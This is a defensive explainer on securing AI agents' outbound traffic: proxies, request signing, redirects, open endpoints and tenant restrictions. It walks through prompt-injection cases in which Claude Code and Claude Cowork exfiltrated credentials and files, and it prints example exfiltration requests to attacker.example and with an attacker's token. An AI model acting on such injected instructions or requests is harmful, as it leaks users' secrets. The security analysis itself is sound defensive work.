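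DPoP doesn't stop an attacker who acts through the client. Fett and colleagues note that malicious code in a web page can get new proofs signed for as long as the page is open. An email containing injected instructions gives an attacker similar power over the shop's assistant. If the email gets the assistant to request a refund, the proxy will sign a valid proof for that request.

Fett and colleagues consider DPoP more robust and straightforward than audience restrictions, which they say have proved too cumbersome for many deployments. The shop can use either method only if its payments service supports it.

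### Signed cloud requests

Amazon's cloud service, AWS, goes a step further and keeps the secret out of the request altogether. The client uses its secret key to calculate a signature, and AWS repeats the calculation to check it. The client doesn't sign with the secret key directly. It first derives a narrower key through HMAC, a function that combines a key with a message to produce a value from which nobody can feasibly recover the key:

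```
DateKey    = HMAC("AWS4" + secret key, date)
RegionKey  = HMAC(DateKey, region)
ServiceKey = HMAC(RegionKey, service)
SigningKey = HMAC(ServiceKey, "aws4_request")
```

If the resulting key leaked, an attacker could use it to sign requests for only one AWS service, in one region, on one day. A newer variant can produce signatures valid in several regions, which is convenient but loosens the region limit.

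According to AWS's signing instructions, the signature covers the HTTP method, path, query, host name, certain headers and a hash of the body. AWS would therefore reject a request signed for `attacker.example`. An attacker who copies a request signed for the right host can resend it, but in most cases only within five minutes of its time stamp. Resending a request to read a file, for example, would give the attacker the file. Changing the body normally invalidates the signature, but the storage service S3 lets a client leave the body unsigned, and an attacker with a copy of such an upload could replace its contents.

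To support this method, a proxy has to calculate the signature itself rather than just replace a placeholder with a secret. It has to do this after making all its other changes to the parts of the request that the signature covers, and it should sign for the host it actually connects to.

### What happened when the key was in a file

Signing protects the secret key only while the agent can't read it. In a February 2026 test, a researcher at Anthropic sent an employee a phishing email that looked like a colleague's request for help and contained a prompt to paste into Claude Code, the company's coding agent. Claude Code could read the AWS credentials file on the employee's machine. Along with ordinary setup steps, the prompt included instructions to read that file, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. The employee ran the prompt. Anthropic then repeated it 25 times, and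 Claude sent out the credentials 24 times.

The 96% result measures how reliably the model carried out one well-disguised prompt after one person had been fooled, not how often phishing attacks would work in general. It also didn't test credential binding, because no proxy had to add a key. A network allowlist would have blocked the upload to an unlisted address, and keeping the file out of the agent's reach would have prevented the theft. These are the two defences Anthropic recommends for this case. It points out that the model's own defences had nothing unusual to detect because the instruction came from the user, and that a human contractor would have done the same.

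### Asking the user

Another way to stop a bad request is to ask a person before the agent acts. Claude Code originally asked for permission before writing files, running commands or using the network. In Anthropic's usage data, people approved about 93% of these prompts.

The 93% figure measures how often users clicked "allow", but doesn't show how often they were wrong to do so. Most of the prompts were presumably for harmless actions, so even careful users would have approved most of them. Anthropic thinks people pay less attention as they see more prompts, which is plausible, but the figure alone doesn't prove it.

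Hard limits can reduce how often an agent has to ask for permission. After Anthropic added a sandbox that denies network access by default and lets the agent work freely inside it, permission prompts fell by 84%. The shop would do better to ask an employee to approve a few large refunds than every web request.

### Relying on the model to refuse

Anthropic also reports that a single attack on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time in Agent Red Teaming, a prompt injection benchmark from Gray Swan. When attackers could make 100 attempts and adapt between them, they succeeded in about 5–6% of cases.

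If each attempt independently succeeds with probability p, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

With p = 0.001 and n = 100, this gives about 9.5%. The measured figure is lower, perhaps because 0.1% is rounded or because every attempt failed in some test scenarios. A domain check, by contrast, returns the same result on every attempt, but if it has a flaw, an attack that exploits the flaw can work every time.

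The figures for newer models come from a different test. TechFeed reports that Anthropic dropped the Agent Red Teaming benchmark because Claude models had come close to its limit, leaving little room to measure improvement. Its replacement uses 1,130 attacks across 28 scenarios. According to Schneier on Security, single attempts on the new benchmark succeeded 0.2% of the time against Claude Opus 5 and 0.5% against Opus 4.8. Because the two tests use different attacks, comparing their results doesn't show whether Opus 5 is easier to fool than Opus 4.7.

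Attack success rates can vary considerably by setting, even for the same model. In a coding environment, an adaptive attacker succeeded against Opus 4.8 on 7.03% of single attempts, or 2.09% with extra safeguards, according to VentureBeat's *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged*. The 7.03% rate is about fourteen times the rate on the benchmark. OpenAI's tests of GPT-5.6 Sol show a similar spread, with success rates of about 0.05% for direct attacks in chat and 3.77% for instructions hidden in material that an agent processes, according to TechRepublic.

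Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every prompt injection test in the card. But in tests of agents without production safeguards, it refused malicious requests less often than any other model Anthropic evaluated. Resistance to prompt injection would therefore help little in a case like the phishing exercise, where the malicious request came from the user.

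## What happens when an approved address redirects the request?

The proxy checks the host name in a request before forwarding it. The service at that host can then reply with a redirect, which sends the client to a different address, possibly on a host the operator never approved.

### How a redirect works

Suppose the assistant asks the payments service for the receipt for charge 1042, and the service keeps its receipts on another host. It replies:

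```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://files.payments.example/receipts/1042
```

A 302 code means that the receipt is temporarily at another address, given in the `Location` header. A client that follows redirects sends a second request to that address and returns the receipt. The calling program often sees only the final reply.

RFC 9110, the HTTP standard, allows clients to follow redirects automatically but doesn't require it. The redirect's status code affects what the client sends next. After a 301 or 302, the client may change a POST request, which submits data, into a GET request, which only asks for data. After a 307 or 308, the client keeps the same method and submits the same data to the new address. If the assistant had posted the customer list to an approved host, a 307 response could cause the client to send the list to a second host.

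The second host can redirect the client again. The Fetch standard, which WHATWG maintains for browsers and which Node.js's `fetch()` also implements, limits a request to 20 redirects.

### Open redirects

The payments service chose where to send the client for the receipt, but an open redirect is a page that sends visitors to any address named in the link. Sites often have such pages to count clicks on outgoing links or to return people to the page they were on before logging in. An attacker can use one without breaking into the site, by writing a link that starts with the site's host name and includes the attacker's address.

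Suppose the code host has a page like this at `/leave`, and an injected email gets the assistant to request it:

```
GET /leave?to=https://attacker.example/ HTTP/1.1
Host: api.code.example
Authorization: Bearer CODE-PLACEHOLDER
```

The code host is on the shop's allowlist, and the operator has bound the host's token to it, so the proxy adds the real token and forwards the request. The code host replies with a 302 redirect to `attacker.example`. The outcome depends on which program follows the redirect.

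When the proxy passes the 302 back to the assistant's web client inside the sandbox, the client writes a new request for `attacker.example`. If the operator has closed every other route out, this request also goes through the proxy, which refuses it because the host isn't on the network allowlist. The client never had the real token, so even if it copies every header, it can send only the placeholder. Without a network allowlist, the proxy would forward the request, still without the token, and the attacker would receive anything the assistant had put in the address.

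A developer may build the proxy on an ordinary HTTP library, and many of these follow redirects by default, as the Fetch standard does. The proxy checks `api.code.example`, adds the token and passes the request to the library. If the code host responds with a 302 redirect to `attacker.example`, the library contacts that address without running the proxy's check again. The request already contains the real token, so the attacker receives it unless the library removes the header that carries it. The assistant then reads the attacker's page as though it came from the code host, and the proxy may log only the approved host.

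**A hosted fetching tool.** Some agents send an address to a tool on another company's servers, which returns the page's contents. The tool's traffic doesn't pass through the shop's proxy, so the shop's allowlist doesn't apply to the original address or the redirect's destination. The company that runs the tool decides whether to check the destination. The tool normally can't leak the shop's tokens because it doesn't have them. If the shop has given it a login for the code host, it could leak that login the same way the proxy could.

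| Who follows the redirect | Is the second host checked? | Does the real credential travel on? |
|---|---|---|
| Client inside the sandbox | Yes, if all traffic must pass through the proxy | No |
| Proxy, through an HTTP library | Not unless the developer adds a check | Depends on the library |
| Hosted fetching tool | Depends on the tool | Only if the tool holds the credential |

The first arrangement is the safest and requires the least new code, because the proxy only has to leave redirects alone. OpenAI's hosted shell may work this way. Its sidecar would protect the token if it checks each request separately, but OpenAI's documentation doesn't explain how the sidecar handles redirects, so a developer should test this with a dummy secret.

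### What the standards say about credentials

Under the HTTP standard published by the RFC Editor, a client that follows a redirect should remove or replace the `Authorization` and `Cookie` headers it generated itself. For headers that the calling program added, the standard advises the client only to "consider removing" those with security implications. This weaker rule applies to a token that a proxy adds before calling an HTTP library.

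The Fetch standard is stricter and requires the client to delete the `Authorization` header as soon as a redirect leads to another origin, meaning a different combination of scheme (such as `https`), host and port. Because the client deletes the header from the request itself, later redirects can't restore it.

Browsers haven't always dropped the `Authorization` header when a redirect leads to another origin. van Kesteren (2019), an editor of the Fetch standard, wrote that credentials a developer had set were copied from request to request. He mentioned a proposal to limit `Authorization` to the first origin, and added that anyone using other headers for credentials was "out of luck". Ishibashi (2023), in *Intent to Ship*, announced the change for Chrome and reported that all browser vendors agreed with it.

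libcurl, the library behind the curl tool, has withheld the `Authorization` header from hosts other than the first in a chain of redirects since version 7.58.0, and has done the same for `Cookie` since 7.64.0. A developer can switch both protections off. Custom headers still go to every host in the chain, as libcurl's manual warns. Many services expect a key in a custom header, such as `X-API-Key`, and a library has no general way to recognize that such a header is secret.

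So if the shop's mail service takes its key in `X-API-Key`, a proxy that follows redirects through libcurl could send the key to any host the mail service redirects to. The HTTP standard advises people who define new headers to document whether clients should remove them on a redirect. Documenting this helps little when one company invented the header for its own service, because a general-purpose library probably won't have a rule for it.

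### Flaws in client libraries

Even the protection for `Authorization` has failed in widely used libraries. These flaws expose only a placeholder if the client is inside the sandbox, but they put the real token at risk if the proxy uses the flawed library to follow redirects.

The first case is follow-redirects, a Node.js library that handles redirects for axios, a popular tool for making web requests. When a redirect led to another domain, the library removed only `Authorization`, `Proxy-Authorization` and `Cookie`, and forwarded all other headers unchanged. GitHub's *follow-redirects leaks Custom Authentication Headers to Cross-Domain Redirect Targets* (2026) describes how a key in `X-API-Key` would reach an attacker's server this way. The flaw affects versions up to 1.15.11, and NIST's *CVE-2026-40895 Detail* confirms that 1.16.0 fixes it. The advisory suggested either removing all non-standard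 headers or letting developers list their sensitive ones. A list protects only the headers included in it, so an operator who upgrades should still test the header their service uses.

The standard HTTP client in Go, a programming language often used for proxies, removed the `Authorization` header when a redirect led to a different domain, but put it back if that domain then redirected to another of its own pages. Go's *Vulnerability Report* (2025) gives the example of a chain from `a.com` to `b.com/1` and then `b.com/2`, where the last request carried the credential meant for `a.com`. An attacker who controlled the second domain could therefore get the credential by adding one more redirect. The flaw affects versions before 1.22.11, versions 1.23.0 to 1.23.4, and early test releases of 1.24. Go's fix keeps the header off for the rest of the chain.

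The third flaw involved `.netrc`, a file that lists logins by host and that curl can read. If the file had an entry for the second host, curl could send that host the bearer token meant for the first, according to curl's *token leak with redirect and netrc* (2026). A `default` entry, which covers hosts without their own entry, was enough to trigger the leak. The flaw affects versions 7.33.0 to 8.18.0 and is fixed in 8.19.0. For people who can't upgrade or patch, the project recommends not using bearer tokens with redirects.

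Curl's developers traced another leak to the same code change. In curl's *bearer token leak on cross-protocol redirect* (2026), curl could send the token to a mail or directory server when a website redirected the request there. The developers rated the leak low severity because it required an unusual setup that deliberately allowed such redirects. The `.netrc` leak seems more relevant to an agent's proxy because it could happen on an ordinary redirect between two websites.

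Libraries have also leaked the logins that clients use for proxies. In 2025, Go fixed a flaw that left proxy credentials in requests redirected outside the original domain. curl's *proxy credentials leak over redirect-to proxy* (2026) describes a flaw in which a redirect from `http://` to `https://` could send one proxy's login to a second proxy. An agent that logs in to its credential-injecting proxy could leak that login in these ways. Keeping the proxy on a private network, as Infisical advises, would make a stolen login harder to use.

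Some HTTP clients intentionally forward credentials to subdomains. Go's *Vulnerability Report* (2024) explains that Go's client keeps the `Authorization` header when `foo.com` redirects to `www.foo.com`, because the second is a subdomain of the first. The follow-redirects code in GitHub's advisory made the same exception. This is convenient when one company runs both hosts, but it is less strict than binding a credential to exact hosts. If a service lets customers run their own subdomains, a redirect could send the shop's token to one of those customers.

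### Data in the address

Removing the token doesn't protect data that the assistant has written into the address. Suppose the injected email tells the assistant to find a customer's phone number and include it in the link:

```
https://api.code.example/leave?to=https://attacker.example/?note=PHONE-NUMBER
```

The code host redirects the client to the address after `to=`, and the client sends the phone number there. The attacker can read the number in the receiving server's log, even if the second request has no credential and the server returns a blank page. A program that checks only the first host would allow the request because that host is approved.

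OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes this kind of leak in ChatGPT. The agent may leak data without writing anything visible to the user, because loading an image or previewing a link also requests an address. According to the post, letting the agent open only well-known sites isn't enough, because many legitimate sites have redirects and an attacker can route a request through one of them. People also browse far more sites than a short list can include, so a strict list would cause frequent warnings, which users might learn to click through without reading.

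Instead, OpenAI checks whether the exact address was already public. It keeps an index of addresses found by a crawler, a program that visits public web pages as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. ChatGPT can load an address automatically if it is in the index. If not, the system prompts the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

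This check would probably catch the link above before the code host redirected anyone. The crawler may have found the `/leave` page, but probably not at an address containing this customer's phone number. The check therefore doesn't depend on recognizing an open redirect. OpenAI doesn't say whether it also checks a redirect's destination. That may matter less than it seems for leaks through the address, because a public link that always redirects to the same place carries nothing from the conversation.

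An attacker could still learn some private data from which public address the agent opens. If the index contained 1,024 of the attacker's addresses, an injected instruction could assign a different value to each one. The address the agent opened would then reveal log₂ 1,024 = 10 bits, enough for a three-digit number. OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain private data. Limiting how many pages an agent may load from an unfamiliar site would slow this kind of leak.

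OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* calls the mechanism Safe Url and says the company also uses it in its Atlas browser and Deep Research tool. When the system detects that a request would send information from a conversation to a third party, it either blocks the request or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. Showing the data seems better than a general warning, since a user can recognize a customer's phone number more easily than a suspicious address.

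The method suits an agent that browses public pages, but it would work badly for the shop's calls to its payments service, because no crawler should ever have seen the address of charge 1042. Those calls need a list of approved hosts that also applies after a redirect.

### Treating each hop as a new request

The simplest fix is for the proxy never to follow redirects. It can return an error or pass the redirect back to the client in the sandbox. Passing it back keeps more services working, because the client can send a new request, which the proxy can check as usual.

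Sometimes the proxy has to follow redirects itself, for example because a custom tool expects a finished reply. For each hop, it should then:

1. stop if the chain has reached a small limit, such as the five redirects that an early HTTP standard recommended;
2. work out the full new address and refuse it unless it uses HTTPS;
3. check the new host against the network allowlist;
4. build a new request without copying any credential from the previous one;
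5. add a credential only if the operator has bound one to the new host.

The proxy would stop the request to `attacker.example` at step 3. Step 4 also covers keys in custom headers if the proxy tracks which headers it filled in, so it no longer has to rely on a library to infer which headers are secret.

Requests that change something need more caution. If the payments service answered a refund request with a 307 redirect, following it would submit the refund details to another address. The HTTP standard warns that a user might not want a client to redirect such a request automatically. The shop's proxy should refuse these redirects and report them, since a payments service has little reason to send a refund request to another host.

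These rules will break some legitimate requests. The receipt from the start of this section is on `files.payments.example`, so the proxy would not fetch it until the operator added that host to the allowlist. If that host also required the payments token, the operator would need to bind the token to both hosts.

Some services avoid the second binding by putting a separate token in the new address. In a discussion of the Fetch standard, Paul Millar says this is popular because the first server can't control which `Authorization` header the client sends next. If the client also sends the original token, the second server receives two credentials, which can make the request fail. Removing the original token protects it and can also make the download work. The token in the address is still a secret, so the proxy shouldn't log it.

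Other programs depend on the old behaviour, which kept the `Authorization` header when a redirect led to another origin. In GitHub's *Authorization-removal change was compatibility-breaking*, developers discuss whether `fetch()` should offer this as an option. An operator who needs it for one service can bind the token to both of that service's hosts instead of turning the protection off everywhere.

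Developers should also check that their redirect settings work as expected. The Fetch standard's `error` mode makes a redirect fail, which suits a payments service. Its `manual` mode returns the redirect but hides its details from the program, so a proxy that relied on it might be unable to read and check the new address. GitHub's *urllib3 does not control redirects in browsers and Node.js* (2025) warns of a similar problem in a popular Python library, which leaves redirects to the browser or Node.js when it runs in either one.

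The operator can test this with a dummy token and two servers they control. The first server is on the allowlist and redirects to the second, which isn't. The second logs every request it receives, so its log should stay empty if the proxy works correctly. To test credential binding separately, the operator can temporarily add the second server to the network allowlist without binding the token to it. The second server should then receive requests without the token, even after it redirects to itself, a step that would have exposed the flaw in Go. The operator should repeat the test with every header that carries a real key.

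OpenAI advises developers who use its shell to record both the hosts an agent requests and the destinations its traffic reaches. The shop could then detect a request to `api.code.example` that ended at `attacker.example`, because the two records would differ.

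## How can an attacker receive data on a domain that is approved?

An attacker can receive data on an approved domain through their own account on that service. The host name identifies the service but not the account that will receive the data. Many customers share `api.code.example`, and the service identifies each one by other parts of the request, usually the credential and sometimes the path. Comparing the requested host with the host that traffic reached therefore wouldn't expose the attacker.

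An attacker can open an account at the code host and create a token for it. Suppose an injected email contains that token and tells the assistant to use it to save the customer list:

```
POST /files HTTP/1.1
Host: api.code.example
Authorization: Bearer ATTACKER-TOKEN
```

The proxy finds the host on the allowlist and forwards the request. The code host accepts the token and stores the file in the attacker's account. There is no redirect, and the logs show an ordinary upload to an approved service.

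### The Claude Cowork disclosure

This happened in January 2026 to Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work. Cowork runs code on the user's desktop in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. The virtual machine could connect only to approved domains. One of them was `api.anthropic.com`, because Cowork can't function without Anthropic's API.

PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of AI products, published *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* two days after Cowork's release. It connected Cowork to a folder of confidential real estate files, then acted as a user who had found a Word file online that looked like a Skill (written instructions that teach Claude a kind of task). The file also contained instructions hidden in tiny white text. When the user asked Cowork to analyze the folder with the Skill, Cowork also read the hidden instructions, which were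 to upload the largest file to Anthropic's file storage using an API key included in the text, which belonged to the attacker's Anthropic account.

Cowork uploaded the file without asking for approval. The attacker could then chat with Claude about the victim's loan estimate, which included financial figures and partial Social Security numbers. In *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, Willison (2026) called the use of the attacker's key a creative workaround.

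PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, a small model, for this demonstration. In a second scenario, a developer gave the stronger Opus 4.5 a malicious guide, and the model uploaded customer records the same way. PromptArmor doesn't report a success rate for either model, and newer models resist injection better. But the allowlist would not have stopped the upload by any model that followed the injected instructions.

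The weakness was older than Cowork. According to PromptArmor, the security researcher Johann Rehberger had reported it in Claude's chat product, and Anthropic had acknowledged it without fixing it. Anthropic warned Cowork's users to watch for suspicious actions that might indicate prompt injection. PromptArmor agreed with Willison that it is unfair to ask this of people who don't program. In the demonstration, users could see the details of the upload only if they expanded the record of a command and understood it.

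### Why credential binding didn't help, and what did

Credential binding, which ties each key to its own service, wouldn't have stopped the upload. It controls the keys that the proxy holds, and this key came from the document. The attacker never used the victim's credentials, which Anthropic says stay in the host computer's keychain, outside the virtual machine.

Anthropic fixed the flaw with a proxy that decrypts traffic to its API and passes only requests carrying the session token issued to that virtual machine. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch data from another address. An injected instruction may still get Cowork to use the session token to upload a file, but the file goes to the user's own account, where the attacker can't read it.

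The new proxy runs inside the virtual machine. Anthropic explains that its servers can't make this check because they can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other API customer. However, an attacker who gained full control of the virtual machine might be able to get around the proxy. A proxy on the host computer that handles only the virtual machine's traffic could presumably make the same check more safely.

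A credential-injecting proxy can achieve much the same result by replacing whatever credential the assistant supplies with the shop's own token, so that the customer list ends up in the shop's account. A proxy that only swaps placeholders would leave the attacker's token unchanged, because that token contains no placeholder. The operator also has to overwrite credentials everywhere a service accepts them. Anthropic's API, for example, accepts a key in the `x-api-key` header, so overwriting only `Authorization` could leave the attacker's key in the request.

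Some approved hosts, such as the parcel company's website, need no credential from the shop. The proxy should remove any login that the assistant adds to a request for these hosts, since the shop can't have issued it.

Before the disclosure, Anthropic had thought of its allowlist as a filter on destinations. This case led it to describe each entry as a capability grant, because approving `api.anthropic.com` had also approved uploads to any Anthropic account. Anthropic says its custom proxy failed, while the virtual machine and other established software did not. The proxy's code seems to have worked as intended, though. It checked the host correctly, but that check didn't restrict which account received the upload.

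In the Cowork case, invisible text supplied an API key and asked for an upload, which is quite a good warning sign. Anthropic's claim that the model's own defences had nothing unusual to detect, which it also makes about its phishing exercise, therefore seems too strong for Cowork.

### Other services that accept data from anyone

An open endpoint is an address on a service that accepts data or commands from anyone, or from anyone with a free account. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) describes several that operators often approve for good reasons.

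**Package registries.** Coding agents need `registry.npmjs.org` to install JavaScript packages. Anyone with a free account can publish a package there, so an injected instruction could make the agent publish a package containing private data. The proxy can prevent this by allowing downloads and refusing publish requests. An internal mirror that only copies packages in would also work, because the agent then wouldn't need to reach the public registry.

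**Public repositories.** An agent may need GitHub to fetch code, but anyone can publish there too. The agent could put data in a public repository or a gist, a page for sharing snippets of text. If the agent's own token can create something public, the attacker doesn't need to supply one, and a check for tokens that aren't the agent's own won't catch the misuse. PromptArmor points out that an attacker can also keep instructions in a file on GitHub and change them during an attack, and the agent will read the new version from an approved host. The operator can limit the agent to the paths of particular repositories.

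**Web forms.** Companies that use Google's office software often approve `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. An attacker can create a form and write a link that fills in and submits an answer. Opening the link sends the data in a GET request without a credential, so allowing only GET requests doesn't prevent this, although it works well for a package registry. The operator could allow only the paths of specific documents, or give the agent a custom tool that reads them.

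Shared hosting lets each customer of a cloud company run a server or store files under the company's domain. If that domain is approved, an attacker can rent space there and read whatever arrives.

| What the service accepts | Whose credential the request needs | A narrower permission |
|---|---|---|
| Packages | The attacker's, or one the agent holds | Downloads only |
| Files and text in public repositories | The attacker's, or one the agent holds | Named repositories, read-only where possible |
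| Answers to a form | None | Named documents, or a custom tool |
| Any request to a rented server | None | The exact host names of the shop's own resources |

PromptArmor suggests asking whether an outsider could use their own API key at a domain, receive submissions there, or get an address there and monitor it. The operator should also ask who controls the domain.

An attacker may be able to receive data through four of the shop's five approved hosts. They could open an account at the payments service, the mail service or the code host, and might be able to store text in a payment description or a draft email. The parcel company may let visitors leave a delivery note for their own parcel. The bank's page of exchange rates is unlikely to be useful to an attacker, because it has no reason to store anything a visitor sends. The shop can't remove the other four hosts, so it has to restrict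 what the assistant can do there.

### Wildcards over shared hosting

A wildcard is a pattern that matches many host names. A developer who wants an agent to reach one storage area on AWS may put the wildcard `*.amazonaws.com` on the allowlist because it's quicker than finding the exact name. But AWS gives other customers' storage areas names under the same domain. In PromptArmor's example, an attacker registers `attacker.s3.amazonaws.com`, and the pattern matches it.

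Microsoft's cloud, Azure, has the same problem. A customer can rent a virtual machine and choose a name for it under `cloudapp.azure.com`, so a pattern covering that domain allows requests to the attacker's machine as well as the shop's. The attacker needs only an ordinary customer account, not a flaw in AWS or Azure.

A wildcard is even more dangerous in a credential binding. If the operator bound a bearer token to `*.cloudapp.azure.com`, the proxy would add the real token to a request to the attacker's machine, giving the attacker the credential as well as the data.

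The fix is to list the exact host name. This works only when the name identifies the tenant. AWS's storage service, S3, also accepts addresses that put the name of the storage area in the path:

```
https://receipts-bucket.s3.amazonaws.com/1042.pdf
https://s3.amazonaws.com/receipts-bucket/1042.pdf
```

Both addresses refer to the same file. The operator can safely approve the first host as long as the shop owns that storage area. Unless the proxy also checks the path, approving the second host would allow requests to every customer's storage reachable there, even though the entry contains no wildcard.

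An approved name can also change owners. If the shop deletes its storage area but leaves the name on the allowlist, somebody else may be able to register that name. The operator should remove the entry before deleting the storage.

### What browsers show about lists of domains

Researchers haven't measured how many agents' allowlists contain an open endpoint, at least not on the scale of a 2016 study of web browsers. A website can send the browser a Content Security Policy (CSP), which may list the hosts from which the page can load scripts. The browser refuses to run scripts from any other host. This is mainly meant to limit cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets their own script into someone else's page.

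In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues searched a Google index of about 106 billion pages from a billion host names. They found CSP on roughly 1.7 million hosts, with 26,011 distinct policies. For each policy, they checked for settings that turned the protection off and compared the approved hosts with a list of domains known to have unsafe endpoints.

They looked for JSONP endpoints and copies of AngularJS. JSONP is an older way of sharing data in which a site returns a script that begins with a function name chosen by the requester. This lets an attacker choose which function to call, or sometimes run any code they like. AngularJS is a popular library that evaluates expressions it finds in a page. An attacker who can add text to the page and load the library from an approved host can get it to run their expression.

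Of the 15 domains that websites approved most often, 14 had an unsafe endpoint, though attackers could use two of those endpoints only if the policy also allowed a risky JavaScript feature. As a result, 75.81% of the distinct policies had a script list that an attacker could bypass. The ten most harmful domains were enough to bypass 68% of all policies. Seven of the ten belonged to Google, where the researchers worked, so a domain's having a reputable owner gave little protection.

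The study's most quoted figure is that 94.72% of policies were ineffective, but most of those policies also allowed scripts written directly into the page, which defeats CSP whatever hosts are on the list. The 2,437 policies without such obvious mistakes are a fairer test of domain lists, and 41.65% of them listed an unsafe domain. Weichselbaum and colleagues consider their figures a lower bound, because an automated search can't find every kind of unsafe endpoint.

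Longer lists were more likely to be bypassable. The median policy approved 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies of that length, although this figure may include policies with other mistakes. The risk grows with each host on a list, much as it does with each repeated injection attempt. If each host independently had a 5% chance of having an unsafe endpoint, a list of 5 hosts would contain at least one about 23% of the time, and a list of 12 about 46%. The study's figures are higher because real hosts aren't independent and the most popular ones were unusually likely to be unsafe.

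These percentages don't apply directly to agents. In a browser, the attacker wants an approved host to return something that runs as code. An agent's attacker usually wants the host to accept data and let someone else read it, and a JSONP endpoint may not store anything. But ordinary text from an approved host can mislead an agent, so more hosts could deliver an attacker's instructions than could deliver a script.

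The JSONP endpoints that made Content Security Policy (CSP) allowlists fail weren't bugs. Their owners had no reason to remove them, since they became a problem only when another website relied on the domain to be safe. The same is true of a package registry that lets anyone publish. Whoever writes the list has to check the endpoints, and the domain's owner can add a new one at any time. *Complex Security Policy*, by Roth, Barron and colleagues, studied the history of CSP on 10,000 highly ranked domains and found that some seemingly secure allowlists contained expired or mistyped domains, which an attacker could register.

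Weichselbaum and colleagues recommended replacing the list of hosts with a nonce, a random value that the website attaches to its own scripts and changes each time it serves the page. The browser runs a script only if it carries the right value, which an attacker can't guess. Anthropic's fix for Cowork similarly requires a token the attacker doesn't have. The protection is weaker for an agent because an injected instruction can make the agent send a request that carries the session token. The token keeps the upload in the right account but doesn't show that the user wanted it.

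### Naming the permitted account

Some services let a company limit which accounts can be used from its network. The company's proxy adds a tenant-restriction header to each request, listing the permitted accounts, and the service refuses requests from any other account. To add the header, the proxy has to terminate TLS, which a credential-injecting proxy already does.

Microsoft's *Configure Custom Headers* (2026) lists such headers for ChatGPT, Claude, GitHub, Google Workspace, Slack and Dropbox, and gives broad patterns such as `*.google.com` for the hosts that should receive them. A wildcard is appropriate here because it applies a restriction, not a permission, to more hosts. The list doesn't explain what each service checks, and differences between those checks matter a good deal for an agent.

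Anthropic's header can block the attacker's upload in the Cowork case. Anthropic's *Enforce network-level access control with Tenant Restrictions* states that the header applies to API keys and OAuth tokens as well as the website and apps. If the attacker's key belonged to an organization that wasn't on the list, Anthropic would reject the upload with a 403 error. This works only if the virtual machine's traffic passes through the company's proxy. The feature is available only to Enterprise plans and organizations that use the developer console, so it wouldn't help someone using Cowork on a personal plan.

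OpenAI's version is narrower. *Corporate Network Controls in ChatGPT Enterprise* tells operators to apply the header only to `chatgpt.com`, and describes a check on which workspaces a user can enter after logging in. It doesn't cover API requests. People can also use ChatGPT without logging in, and the operator has to block that separately by its path. The desktop and mobile apps accept only certain certificates, so they won't work through a decrypting proxy until the company adds its own certificate to their list.

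OpenAI's *IP allowlist* explains that an organization can have OpenAI reject API requests from untrusted network addresses, even if they carry a valid key. That would stop a thief from using the shop's key at home, but it wouldn't stop the assistant from using an attacker's key, because the attacker's organization sets its own rules about where its keys work.

GitHub's restriction became generally available in September 2025. GitHub's *Enterprise access restrictions with corporate proxies is now generally available* (2025) describes it as covering the website and API, and GitHub's *Enterprise access restrictions now supports multiple enterprises* (2025) also lists git requests and a limit of 20 enterprises per header. The restriction works only for companies whose accounts are what GitHub calls Enterprise Managed Users, so a small company with ordinary accounts can't use it. GitHub also offers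 some customers their own subdomain of `GHE.com`, which lets an ordinary allowlist tell the company's account from an attacker's by host name.

Microsoft does part of the enforcement at sign-in. *Universal Tenant Restrictions* (2026), a copy of another Microsoft page, describes this for outside apps that use Microsoft's login, and Cato Networks' *Managing Tenant Restrictions for SaaS Apps (Tenant Restrictions Policy)* tells operators to select Microsoft's login application when they set up the rule for Microsoft 365. This check can stop an employee from logging in to a personal account, but it would probably miss an attacker's token in an injected instruction, since the attacker has already signed in elsewhere.

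| Service | What the operator names | Documented coverage | Main gap for an agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude | Organization | Website, apps, API keys and OAuth tokens | Personal plans |
| ChatGPT | Workspace | `chatgpt.com` | API requests |
| GitHub | Enterprise | Website, API and git | Ordinary accounts |
| Outside apps with Microsoft login | Tenant | Sign-in | Tokens obtained elsewhere |

All these headers depend on the proxy. Anthropic's *Tenant restrictions*, written for a separate version of Claude for government agencies, states that a request without the header is not restricted. An agent that can reach the service without going through the proxy therefore avoids the check.

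An agent that runs code can also write the header itself and name the attacker's account. The proxy must remove that header before setting its own. If the proxy only adds its own header, ordinary traffic still works, so the operator may not notice the mistake. Anthropic's test configures the proxy to name a tenant the operator doesn't own, then has the client send a header naming the operator's real tenant. The request should fail with a 403 error. A 400 error means that both headers reached the server, and a successful request means that the server used the client's header.

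The shop should run a second test for each approved service, whether or not the service uses a tenant header. The operator opens a spare account on the service, then uses that account's key to try to upload a harmless file to the account from the assistant's environment. If the upload succeeds, an attacker's would too.

Tenant headers don't cover endpoints that need no account. Restricting Google Workspace to the shop's own domain might not block an anonymous response to an attacker's form, so the operator should test that as well. npm also isn't on Microsoft's list.

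### Data perimeters in the cloud

AWS can check both the account making a request and the owner of the resource it targets. AWS's *Establish permissions guardrails using data perimeters* defines a data perimeter as a set of rules that let only trusted identities access trusted resources from expected networks. An identity is a user or program with an AWS login, and a resource might be an S3 bucket (a storage area).

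Suppose the shop runs its assistant in a private network on AWS. The network connects to S3 through a VPC endpoint, a private link with its own access policy. The operator can write two conditions into that policy. `aws:PrincipalOrgID` requires the caller to belong to the shop's organization, and `aws:ResourceOrgID` requires the bucket to belong to it. Together they produce these results:

| Whose credential | Whose bucket | Result |
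|---|---|---|
| The shop's | The shop's | Allowed |
| The shop's | The attacker's | Refused because of the bucket |
| The attacker's | The shop's | Refused because of the caller |
| The attacker's | The attacker's | Refused on both grounds |

The bottom row shows the Cowork attack applied to S3. AWS mentions that employees might do the same, using their own credentials to put company data in their own storage. A host name check allows all four requests because they can all go to the same S3 address.
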